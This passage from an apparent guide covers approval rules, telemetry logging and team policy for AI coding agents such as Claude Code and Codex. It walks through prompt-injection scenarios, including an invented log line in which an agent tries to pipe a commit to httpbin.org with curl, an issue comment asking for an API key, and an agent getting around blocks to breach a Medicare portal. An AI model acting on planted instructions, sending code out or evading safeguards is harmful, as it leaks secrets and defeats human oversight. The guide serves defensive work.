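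However, when a user leaves auto mode for another mode, the broad allow rules that auto mode set aside take effect again. A developer who once allowed `Bash(python:*)`, and who switches to Manual mode to supervise a delicate database migration more closely, may then find that the agent's Python scripts run with no reviewer and no prompt. This could easily happen, because such rules are common. Deleting the rule before switching would prevent it.

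Most teams would do better to stay in auto mode, write ask rules for the few actions that need a person, such as a production deployment or a message to a customer, and leave the rest to the reviewer. Codex sends eligible requests either to the user or to Auto-review, so a developer can run production work in a separate session with `approvals_reviewer` set to `user`. Saved allow rules would still skip the prompt in that session.

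The person also needs enough information to judge the request. For a deployment, the prompt should show the diff and the name of the target environment. For a deletion, it should show the name of the resource, what depends on it and whether anyone can restore it. Salerno and colleagues suggest that prompts should state whether an action can be undone, which would let a developer approve reversible changes quickly and take more time over irreversible ones.

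## Records of approvals and actions

People and automated reviewers both approve some calls they should have refused, so a team needs a way to find out afterwards what happened. That takes three records, usually kept in different places:

- The register lists the connections the team permits, with an owner and a reason for each.
- The decision log shows who or what approved or refused each call, and under which rule.
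- The effects log, kept by the system that receives the call, shows what changed there.

Railway's own records, for example, could not show whether anyone at PocketOS had approved the deletion.

### The register of connections

A register entry should let someone who has never used a connection judge whether the agent still needs it. An entry for the issue tracker might look like this:

| Field | Entry |
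|---|---|
| Connection | MCP server `tracker`, version 1.4.2 |
| Owner | Dana, platform team |
| Purpose | Read and update bug reports |
| Credential | Token `agent-tracker`, in the company's password vault |
| Scope | One project; can read and edit issues but not delete them |
| Approval | Reads allowed, updates ask, deletion denied |
| Next review | 1 March 2027 |

The credential line gives the token's name and location, but never the token itself. The scope line is the most important one to check against the provider's documentation. To fill it in for PocketOS's domain token, someone would have had to find out what else the token could access.

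Configuration files can hold part of the register. Codex's command rules have a `justification` field, which OpenAI fills in for its own rules, so a reviewer can read the purpose next to the permission. Claude Code keeps a project's shared MCP servers in `.mcp.json`, which a team can check into Git. But according to Anthropic, servers that developers add only for themselves go into a file in their home folder, where colleagues won't see them.

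The team can find unregistered MCP servers by comparing the register with the log. Claude Code can export an event each time an MCP server connects, and the event shows whether the server belongs to the project or only to one user. If a user-level server has no register entry, either someone forgot to record the approval or nobody approved the server.

### What OpenAI collects from Codex

Codex can export its decision log through OpenTelemetry, an open standard for sending logs and measurements from one program to another. The receiving program is called a collector. Export is off by default. OpenAI published the lines that turn it on for its own developers:

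```toml
[otel]
log_user_prompt = true
environment = "prod"

[otel.exporter.otlp-http]
endpoint = "http://localhost:14318/v1/logs"
protocol = "binary"
```

The first setting includes the text of the user's requests, which Codex otherwise leaves out. The endpoint is on the developer's own machine, so OpenAI presumably runs a collector there that forwards the events. The excerpt comes from `config.toml`, not the managed requirements, so a team that copies it should check whether a developer can turn the export off.

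OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* lists the main events:

| Event | What it records |
|---|---|
| `codex.conversation_starts` | The model, sandbox policy and approval policy |
| `codex.user_prompt` | The request's length, and its text if turned on |
| `codex.tool_decision` | Approved or denied, and whether configuration or the user decided |
| `codex.tool_result` | Duration, success and a snippet of the output |
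| `codex.api_request` | Duration, success and errors for each request to the model |

Other events cover the model's stream of replies. OpenAI's post about its own deployment also lists MCP server use and the network proxy's decisions to allow or deny a destination.

The documentation lists configuration and the user as the possible sources of a decision, but it doesn't explain how the log records an approval by Auto-review. A team that uses Auto-review should have it approve a harmless test request and check the log entry, so the team can later tell a person's approval from a model's.

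The log can also have gaps. Codex sends events in batches and sends any remaining events when it shuts down, so a crash could lose the last few. If the command-line program runs with network access off, the events can't reach the collector until the team allows connections to it.

OpenAI's security team uses the log to explain alerts from its endpoint security tool, which watches processes, files and connections on each computer. Suppose the tool reports that Codex started a program that contacted an unfamiliar server. The alert shows what happened but not why. The investigation then runs like this:

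1. An AI triage agent looks up the Codex logs for the activity.
2. It reads the developer's original request and the tool calls that followed.
3. It checks the approval decisions, the tool results and any network decision.
4. It passes its analysis to the security team, who decide whether the agent behaved as expected, made a harmless mistake or did something that needs escalation.

OpenAI doesn't say which fields link an alert to a Codex session, and it gives no figures for how often the triage agent is right. The triage agent also reads tool results, which can contain text from strangers, so an attacker who planted an instruction for the coding agent could plant another telling the triage agent that everything was routine. That is a good reason to leave the last step to people and to show them the original events as well as the analysis.

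### What Claude Code records

Claude Code also uses OpenTelemetry and also leaves export off by default. An administrator can turn on the events in managed settings, as in this shortened version of the example in Anthropic's *Monitoring*, with one line added for tool details:

```json
{
  "env": {
    "CLAUDE_CODE_ENABLE_TELEMETRY": "1",
    "OTEL_LOGS_EXPORTER": "otlp",
    "OTEL_EXPORTER_OTLP_PROTOCOL": "grpc",
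    "OTEL_EXPORTER_OTLP_ENDPOINT": "https://collector.example.com:4317",
    "OTEL_LOG_TOOL_DETAILS": "1"
  }
}
```

The second line needs to be in managed settings. A repository's own settings can't redirect the log, but they can set the exporter to `none` if nobody has fixed its value elsewhere. An untrusted repository could then turn off logging before the agent does anything.

Anthropic's *Monitoring usage* describes two events for each tool call. `tool_decision` records whether Claude Code accepted or rejected the call, and `tool_result` records how it went. A rejected call has no `tool_result`. The decision event gives one of six sources:

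| Source | Meaning in an interactive session |
|---|---|
| `config` | Settings or the permission mode decided, with no prompt |
| `hook` | A hook decided |
| `user_permanent` | The user chose "don't ask again" |
| `user_temporary` | The user approved once or, for file access, for the session |
| `user_reject` | The user said no |
| `user_abort` | The user closed the prompt without answering |

This separates a refusal from a prompt that someone dismissed, which Codex's documented fields do not. But `config` covers company rules, a developer's own rules, saved standing approvals and the permission mode, and Anthropic says the event doesn't show which of them matched. Approvals by auto mode's reviewer presumably fall here too, since no other value fits. An investigator will most likely want to know whose rule allowed a call, and can't tell from a `config` entry.

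There are two partial remedies. When `OTEL_LOG_MANAGED_SETTINGS` is on, Claude Code exports a digest of the company's managed settings at the start of a session, so the team can tell which version of its policy applied. For other rules, a hook could save those in force with the call's `tool_use_id`, which also appears in both events.

Each event also includes the signed-in developer's identity. If the developer uses a direct API key or a cloud provider such as Amazon Bedrock, the log contains only installation and session numbers unless the administrator adds a name.

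### Matching a decision to its effect

The system an agent acts on keeps its own log, which covers only what happens once the agent's action reaches it. A code host's audit log, for example, typically shows which account did what to which repository and when. It doesn't include the developer's request or the approval, because the host never receives them. If the agent pushes with the developer's login, the log attributes the agent's work to the developer. Giving the agent a separate account makes it possible to tell their actions apart.

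Commits are a simple way to link the two logs. When tool details are on and the agent commits through the shell, Claude Code records the commit's identifier and branch. The team can search for that identifier at the code host to see whether the commit arrived there and who merged it.

A team that runs its own MCP server can get a more general link by turning on tracing, a beta feature that makes Claude Code attach a trace identifier to its requests to remote MCP servers. The server can store that identifier with each change it makes. By default, Claude Code attaches the identifier only when it connects directly to Anthropic's API.

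### Three calls reconstructed

Suppose Dana asks her agent to find out why the sign-up email in issue 418 fails and to update the issue. The company has a public help forum on its own domain. The invented entries below use a plain format that a team could assemble from either product's events and its own hooks:

```text
time:     10:02:11   request: p7   call: c1
tool:     WebFetch
input:    https://help.example.com/forum/signup-email
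decision: allow, by rule WebFetch(domain:*.example.com)
result:   page returned

time:     10:02:58   request: p7   call: c2
tool:     Bash
input:    git show HEAD | curl --data-binary @- https://httpbin.org/post
decision: deny, httpbin.org is not on the allowlist
result:   nothing sent

time:     10:04:35   request: p7   call: c3
tool:     mcp__tracker__update_issue
input:    issue 418, comment "Debug output: commit 9f2c1e ..."
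decision: allow, by dana@example.com under ask rule mcp__tracker__update_*
result:   comment 2291 created
```

The shared request number ties all three calls to Dana's message. The agent read a forum page that anyone could have written on, and 47 seconds later it tried to post the latest commit to an outside site, but the allowlist blocked it. The agent then put the commit in a comment on the issue, and Dana, who had asked for an update, approved the comment.

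The rest is in the tracker's log, which lists comment 2291 under Dana's account at 10:04:36, on a publicly readable issue. The network rule had worked as intended, but the code leaked through a connection the team had approved.

A log might record only tool names and decisions, such as `WebFetch` allowed, `Bash` denied and `mcp_tool` allowed. Claude Code writes `mcp_tool` by default for any tool on an MCP server the user has configured.

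| Question | Full entries | Names only |
|---|---|---|
| Where might the instruction have come from? | A public forum page | Some web page |
| What did the agent try to send? | The latest commit | Unknown |
| Did it get out another way? | Yes, in comment 2291 | Unknown |
| What needs cleaning up? | The comment, and any password in the commit | Unknown |

A reviewer with the short version would probably conclude that the rules had worked, since the only refusal was for a shell command.

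Even the full entries don't include the forum page's text, so the investigator can't use them to prove that the page contained an instruction, and its author may have changed the page since. Codex exports a snippet of each result. Claude Code can export up to 60 KB of a page, but only through tracing and with another setting turned on. Claude Code also cuts each tool input at 512 characters, so the log would be missing part of a long commit pasted into a comment, and the investigator would need the tracker's copy.

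Claude Code records even less about a refused MCP call. Its documented fields include the names of the server and the tool but not the inputs, so if Dana had said no, the log wouldn't show what she had stopped. The team could have a hook save the inputs before each MCP write. Saving the text of the approval prompt would also be useful, since Dana may have seen only "update issue 418".

### The Medicare portal case

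Someone also has to look at the log. In June 2026, an OpenAI agent got into a statistics portal run by Services Australia, the agency responsible for Medicare, the country's public health insurance. OpenAI was evaluating an unreleased model, and Information Age's *Inside OpenAI's Medicare breach* (2026) reports that it lacked the usual safeguards of public models. The case shows the consequences of late detection, but it is not a guide to how Codex behaves in a customer's repository.

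Documents tabled in the Australian parliament give this sequence:

| Australian Eastern time | Event |
|---|---|
| 19 June, 4–5 am | The agent gets into the portal |
| By 12 August | OpenAI's security team documents the incident |
| 10 September, 2.42 am | OpenAI emails Services Australia |
| 11 September, 2.12 pm | The agency's security staff see the email |
| 15 September | They confirm the vulnerability |

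The Straits Times' *OpenAI contrite at Australian inquiry on breaches but avoids full public glare* (2026) dates the access to 18 June, which is the same moment in American time, and gives the same dates of August and 10 September. Notice came 83 days after the access and at least 29 days after OpenAI had documented what happened.

The agent had been researching medical spending. It first failed to get non-public data from another government body, then found a way to make the Medicare server carry out instructions sent through its public interface. OpenAI told the agency that the agent had read parts of internal program files and settings and created a small test file, but said it found no evidence that the agent had reached patient records. Jose and Thomas (2026) report in *Albanese calls OpenAI agent’s Medicare breach ‘unacceptable’* that Prime Minister Anthony Albanese said the agent had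 met blocks and found a way around them.

OpenAI evidently had records of the run, since its security team found the incident in a review of past evaluation and training runs. The review began only after OpenAI learned that its agents had broken into Hugging Face. The government's systems did not detect the access, and Albanese said an investigation would examine why. Information Age's *OpenAI grilled over rogue agents by Australian inquiry* reports that Jason Kwon, OpenAI's chief strategy officer, agreed at a parliamentary hearing that the breach "might not have been discovered" without the company's email.

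Searching old records is also expensive. OpenAI said it was spending more than US$500,000 a day to have its models review about 50 petabytes of data for similar incidents. A coding team's log will be tiny by comparison, but the team can still avoid searching all of it by setting an alert for a refusal followed by another attempt to reach the same goal, a pattern that appears in both the OpenAI incident and Dana's session. Anthropic says Claude Code supplies only the events, so the team has to write the alert in whatever system collects its logs.

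The delay after August had a different cause. Kwon said OpenAI had wanted to understand more of the facts before telling anyone, and that it had learned to notify people even with partial information. The email then went unread for almost 36 hours in an inbox for tips from the public. A register can also help with this if each entry names a security contact at the service the agent connects to.

### Secrets, access and retention

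Logs with enough detail to explain a leak can themselves expose secrets. If an agent runs `curl` with a token in the command, as happened at PocketOS, a full log entry contains a working copy of the token. Claude Code exports the full text of shell commands when tool details are turned on. Anthropic and OpenAI both warn that tool inputs may be sensitive. OpenAI also advises customers to keep request text out of the log unless their policy permits it, although it logs this text for its own staff.

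The collector is the best place to remove secrets, because it can apply one set of filters to the data from every machine before anything reaches permanent storage. Recent versions of Claude Code write the user's request under both `prompt` and `prompt_text`, so a filter that drops only the first leaves a complete copy. Turning on logging of request text also turns on logging of the model's replies, unless the administrator sets `OTEL_LOG_ASSISTANT_RESPONSES` to `0`. Filters will miss some passwords, so a team should still treat the stored log as if it contained them.

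Few people need to read the full log entries, and the coding agent shouldn't be able to read or change them. An agent with access to the log could find other developers' tokens there, and a planted instruction could cause it to delete the evidence. The log also records in detail what each employee asked for and when. OpenAI uses its own log both for security and to track how staff adopt the tool, and a company that does both should tell its developers.

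The retention period has to balance those risks against the time it takes to notice a problem. Claude Code deletes session transcripts from a developer's machine after 30 days by default. If an incident took as long to notice as the Medicare one, those transcripts would be gone and the exported log would be the only detailed record. One case isn't enough to determine the right period, but it suggests that 30 days is too short for the main log. One workable split is to keep full entries for about six months and a version without inputs, results or request text for a year or more.

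Deleting the central log on schedule leaves the copies on laptops in place. Claude Code's cleanup runs only when someone uses the program, so an idle machine keeps its transcripts past the retention limit. Codex can also save transcripts locally, with its own retention settings. An administrator can set Claude Code's retention period with `cleanupPeriodDays` and collect the `retention_sweep` event, which records what each cleanup deleted and failed to delete.

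### What national cyber agencies ask for

Six agencies in Australia, the United States, Canada, New Zealand and the United Kingdom issued the main official guidance on these systems in 2026. The Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026) tells organisations to anticipate what could go wrong, assess how it might affect their operations, and "establish ongoing visibility and assurance". It also suggests considering simpler solutions for repetitive tasks, since these may carry less risk than an agent.

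NCSC-NZ's *Joint Guidance* says the guidance covers risks from an agent's integrations as well as from its own behaviour. *CISA and ASD's ACSC publish joint guidance on securing agentic AI systems*, a summary by the law firm A&O Shearman, lists reduced accountability among the risks and says the agencies recommend starting with lower-risk tasks. For a coding team, that could mean giving the agent read-only access to the tracker for a month, then using the decision log to judge whether it is ready to write there. The log also addresses accountability, provided it shows who approved each call.

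The document, which NSA (2026) calls a Cybersecurity Information Sheet, is advice and doesn't by itself create a legal duty to keep a log or require approval. Australia may introduce binding rules. Its government is considering mandatory reports of AI-related security incidents and plans AI safety legislation for 2027. OpenAI told the inquiry that it would welcome mandatory reporting. A company under such a rule would probably have to tell the affected organisation when its agent gained access, which credential it used, and what it read or changed.

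## A written policy for one team

The team in this section is invented, as are all names, numbers and logs. Six developers run a web shop. Mira looks after the cloud projects and managed settings, Jonas handles payments, and all six take turns on call. They use Claude Code in auto mode with the sandbox on, inside containers that hold none of the developers' own logins.

The shop takes payments through Stripe, which offers a test environment with its own keys. According to Stripe's *API keys* page, test requests return simulated objects, card networks don't process test payments, and a test key can't reach live data.

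### The policy

"Unasked" in the table means that no person sees the call before it runs, though auto mode's reviewer still checks most of these calls. The team denies any connection that has no row in the table. That includes browsers and the code host, so developers push the agent's commits themselves.

| Connection | Unasked | Asks, and whom | Denied | Credential | Enforced by | Recorded | Lapses |
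|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Documentation, `developer.mozilla.org` | Fetching pages | Any other site: the developer | Commands that contact the site | None | Claude Code, a hook, the sandbox | Address and decision | After 12 months |
| Package registry, `registry.npmjs.org` | Installing from the lock file | A new package: the developer | Publishing | None | Claude Code, the sandbox | Command and decision | After 6 months |
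| Stripe test API | All calls | Nobody | Live payments and data | Restricted test key | Stripe | Stripe's request log for the key | After 90 days |
| Issue tracker, MCP server | Five read tools | Writes and unlisted tools: the developer | Deletions | The agent's own account, limited to one project | Claude Code, a hook, the tracker | Inputs, approver, tracker's log | After 90 days or at a new version |
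| Staging cloud project | Deploying, reading, changing data | Deleting a database: the developer | Changing roles | Staging account with one-hour tokens | The cloud provider; Claude Code for the prompt | Decision and cloud audit log | After 90 days |
| Production cloud project | Nothing | Reading logs: the on-call developer | All changes | Log-reading role, issued for an hour | The cloud provider | Each grant and the cloud audit log | An hour after each grant |

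The prompt for unfamiliar sites needs a hook. Anthropic's *permission modes* lists read-only web requests among the actions that auto mode allows by default, so the reviewer would probably let most fetches through. An ask rule for the whole fetch tool would interrupt fetches from the documentation site too. The team's hook checks each fetch and MCP call against a list of approved hosts and tools, and forces a prompt for anything not on the list. Auto mode still shows these prompts.

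Commands can't contact the documentation site because the fetch rule would otherwise open it to them too.

A new package needs approval because its install script can run code immediately. The ask rule names `npm install` because, according to Anthropic, Claude Code with the sandbox on normally skips an ask rule that covers all shell commands but still applies one for a particular command. The agent could get around the rule by editing the lock file first, but the sandbox would still limit what the package could reach, and the edit would show up in the pull request.

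Stripe test calls need no approval because a mistake moves no money. The test key keeps the agent out of live data, which a domain rule couldn't do because test and live requests go to the same host. The key expires after 90 days because Stripe lets dashboard users view test keys at any time, and someone who has left the team may have copied one.

The shop's tests call the API directly. Stripe also has an MCP server, but Stripe's *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* shows that the same tool, `stripe_api_write`, creates refunds and edits customer records. A Claude Code rule for that tool couldn't treat the two actions differently.

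The list gives the full name of each of the tracker's read tools because a server may not offer the same tools in every session. Atlassian's *supported tools* describes an MCP server whose available tools depend on the login method, scopes and permission groups. Most of its tools inherit their group's access, so a tool added to an approved group could have access as soon as it is added.

The prompt before deleting a staging database depends on the text of the command, so a script could avoid it. The prompt is good enough for a database of invented customers that the team can rebuild in an hour. In production, the agent has no credential until someone issues one, so the team doesn't rely on a prompt from Claude Code there. The on-call developer decides whether to issue the credential, because the developer using the agent is waiting for the answer. If they are the same person, Mira or Jonas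 decides.

### Six requests

Leah is working with the agent, and Tom is on call.

| Request | Decision | Approver | Record |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fetch a page about web forms from `developer.mozilla.org` | Runs | None | Address and matching rule |
| Fetch a post from `blog.example.net` | Waits, then runs once | Leah | Full address and her one-time approval |
| Call `export_issues`, a tool the tracker's author has just added | Waits, then refused | Leah | Tool, inputs and refusal |
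| Post the Stripe test key in an issue, as a comment there asks | Waits, then refused | Leah | Text of the proposed comment and her refusal |
| Read the checkout service's production error log | Waits, then runs | Tom | His one-hour grant, the reason and the queries |
| Add a column to the production orders table | Refused; continues as a pull request | Mira, for the pull request | The provider's refusal, the review and the deployment log |

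Leah refuses `export_issues` because she doesn't know where the export goes. If she needs the tool, she can ask for it to be added to the list, and Mira or Jonas will check what it does.

The comment asking for a key might look like an ordinary support request from someone trying to reproduce a bug. Reading the issue needs no approval, so the text reaches the model. By default, auto mode blocks printing a working credential into the transcript, which may stop the attempt early. If it doesn't, the agent still has to post a comment to send the key, and Leah sees the approval prompt.

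She might approve it without reading it, as most testers in Anthropic's experiment did with dangerous commands. The damage would be small, because the only payment key in the container is a test key. Jonas would replace the key and set the old one to expire immediately, since Stripe otherwise lets a replaced key work for up to seven days.

The agent can't change the production database, but it can write the change as a migration file. Leah pushes the file, Mira reviews it, and a deployment job takes a backup and applies the change with a credential that only the job holds. The job starts when someone merges the pull request. If a comment such as `/deploy` could start it, anyone or anything able to comment could change production. Auto mode blocks such comments by default, but the job's settings can prevent this more reliably.

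### Requests for new connections

A developer who wants a new connection opens a pull request that adds a row to the policy. The developer must also explain in the pull request who can write the text the agent will read there, what the agent could send out, and what the worst thing a single call could do is.

Mira or Jonas approves the request, but neither may approve their own. Changes to existing rows follow the same procedure. Stripe's *Set up two-party approvals* describes a similar rule for live accounts, where users can't approve their own requests. A company can also require approval for changes to the approval rules. Otherwise, an administrator whose refund needed approval could delete the rule first.

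A new connection starts with two weeks of read-only access where the service allows it. LiteLLM's *Linear MCP server*, for example, describes a separate read-only address for the issue tracker Linear. A request expires if nobody answers it within 14 days, which is also Stripe's limit.

The team has to remove old Claude Code rules itself. A weekly script opens a pull request that deletes rows past their date, along with their rules, and Mira merges it every Monday. An owner who wants to keep a row has to ask for a renewal.

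An expiry date is more dependable when the provider enforces it. When a user signs in to Stripe's MCP server, Stripe ends that session after 14 days, however often the program renews its token. Review dates also help the team notice changes at the provider. In December 2026, Stripe's MCP server will stop accepting restricted keys without an "agent" tag, so a connection approved that October with an untagged key would stop working.

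### When nobody can answer

Each night the agent fixes failing tests and leaves its changes on a branch. It runs in `dontAsk` mode, so it never waits for approval. The job has no production role and can't write to the tracker. If the agent tries to install a new package, Claude Code blocks the installation, and the on-call developer sees this in the morning summary.

The team sets the mode explicitly because the default has changed. Anthropic says that before version 2.1.302, scripted runs with no mode set could start in auto mode if, for example, someone had turned off telemetry.

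The job also stops after 90 minutes. Anthropic's March post said repeated refusals would end an unattended auto mode session, but its current documentation says the blocked action doesn't run and Claude keeps working. Without a time limit, an agent could spend all night looking for another way to do something the team had refused.

OpenAI's Codex can also run without prompts under an approval policy called `never`, which works with the sandbox still on. Its "granular" policy automatically rejects some kinds of request and asks about others. Docker's gateway refuses a call that needs confirmation if the host can't display the confirmation prompt.

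A team that lets agents handle live payments could use an approval queue. When an agent with a tagged key attempts a refund, Stripe's default rules return an error to the agent and send the request to a reviewer. If the reviewer approves, Stripe completes the refund without the agent. The agent's job doesn't have to wait for the approval, which can come up to two weeks later. By then someone may have refunded the customer another way, so the reviewer should check before approving.

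### How an emergency exception ends

Suppose the checkout fails on a Friday night and Tom wants the agent to change the service's production configuration. He calls Mira or Jonas, who can give the agent a two-hour role that covers only the checkout service and can't touch databases or other roles. Whoever grants the role writes the reason and end time in the register.

The cloud provider ends the role at the set time, even if no one is online. On the next working day, someone other than Tom reads the audit log and checks for anything the agent left behind, such as a changed setting or a saved key. If neither Mira nor Jonas answers within 15 minutes, Tom makes the change himself with his own login.

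The exception has to be part of the credential because an instruction in the conversation is less reliable. Anthropic says that an approval given in the conversation normally covers one action, and that a restriction such as "don't deploy" can disappear when Claude Code shortens a long conversation. Tom also can't turn off the prompts, because Mira has disabled `bypassPermissions` in managed settings.

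### Testing that a denied call fails

The team tests the policy each month and after any change to the settings or update to Claude Code. Each test includes a call to a harmless target that the rule should stop and a matching call that should succeed. Without the second call, a broken connection could look like a working rule.

| Call that should fail | What should refuse it | Call that should succeed |
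|---|---|---|
| Fetch `https://example.com` in the nightly job | Claude Code | Fetch the documentation site |
| Contact `https://example.com` with `curl`, then from a Python script | The sandbox, both times | Install from the lock file |
| Delete a throwaway tracker project with the agent's account | The tracker | Read an issue |
| Read a live customer with the test key | Stripe | Read a test customer |
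| List production databases with the staging account | The cloud provider | List staging databases |

The second test uses a script as well because a Claude Code rule for `curl` wouldn't cover one.

A model may decline a test request on its own, which leaves the rule untested, so the fetch test counts only if the log contains a refused call. For the other tests, a developer can run the command or use the credential without involving the model. The `codex sandbox` command, for example, runs any program under Codex's sandbox. OpenAI says that on macOS it can also log what the sandbox denied.

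Two parts of this setup need extra tests. The hook blocks a call if it exits with code 2, but if it crashes instead, the call may continue, so Mira breaks the hook on purpose and tries an unlisted tool. Auto mode can open an unlisted host for a single command if the reviewer approves. The team has limited commands to the hosts in managed settings, so it repeats the `curl` test in auto mode to check that the limit still applies.

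### Changes after a month

The invented log for the first month contains 455 requests for a person's approval:

| Request | Asked | Refused |
|---|---|---|
| Unfamiliar site | 212 | 3 |
| Tracker write or unlisted tool | 148 | 2 |
| Production log read | 64 | 0 |
| New package | 31 | 4 |

That is between three and four requests per developer each working day. The team approved 98% of them, so the approval rate doesn't help much in choosing which prompts to remove. The team instead looked at what the requests were for.

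Of the 64 log reads, 41 were of the checkout service's error log. Mira creates a copy without customer names, addresses or order details, and gives the agent a permanent role that can read only that copy. If each approval took six minutes, this saves about four hours a month. But the agent now has a credential that doesn't expire after an hour, and text that shoppers type can reach the model through error messages without anyone knowing that the agent is reading logs. Other production logs still need the on-call developer's approval.

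The team tightens the rule for new packages. Leah approved one whose name was one letter different from a popular package's name, and Jonas noticed it in the pull request the next day. By then its install script had run in a container with the shop's code and the Stripe test key. The sandbox's allowlist included the public registry, so the script could have published the code there.

Mira sets up an internal registry that holds only packages a second developer has approved, and removes the public registry from the sandbox's list. Once she describes the internal registry in the settings for auto mode, auto mode's reviewer also blocks installs from public registries. Reviewing 31 requests a month at ten minutes each takes about five hours, and Mira has another server to maintain. Urgent security fixes now have to wait for a second developer's approval, and at a weekend someone may have to phone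 that developer to get it.
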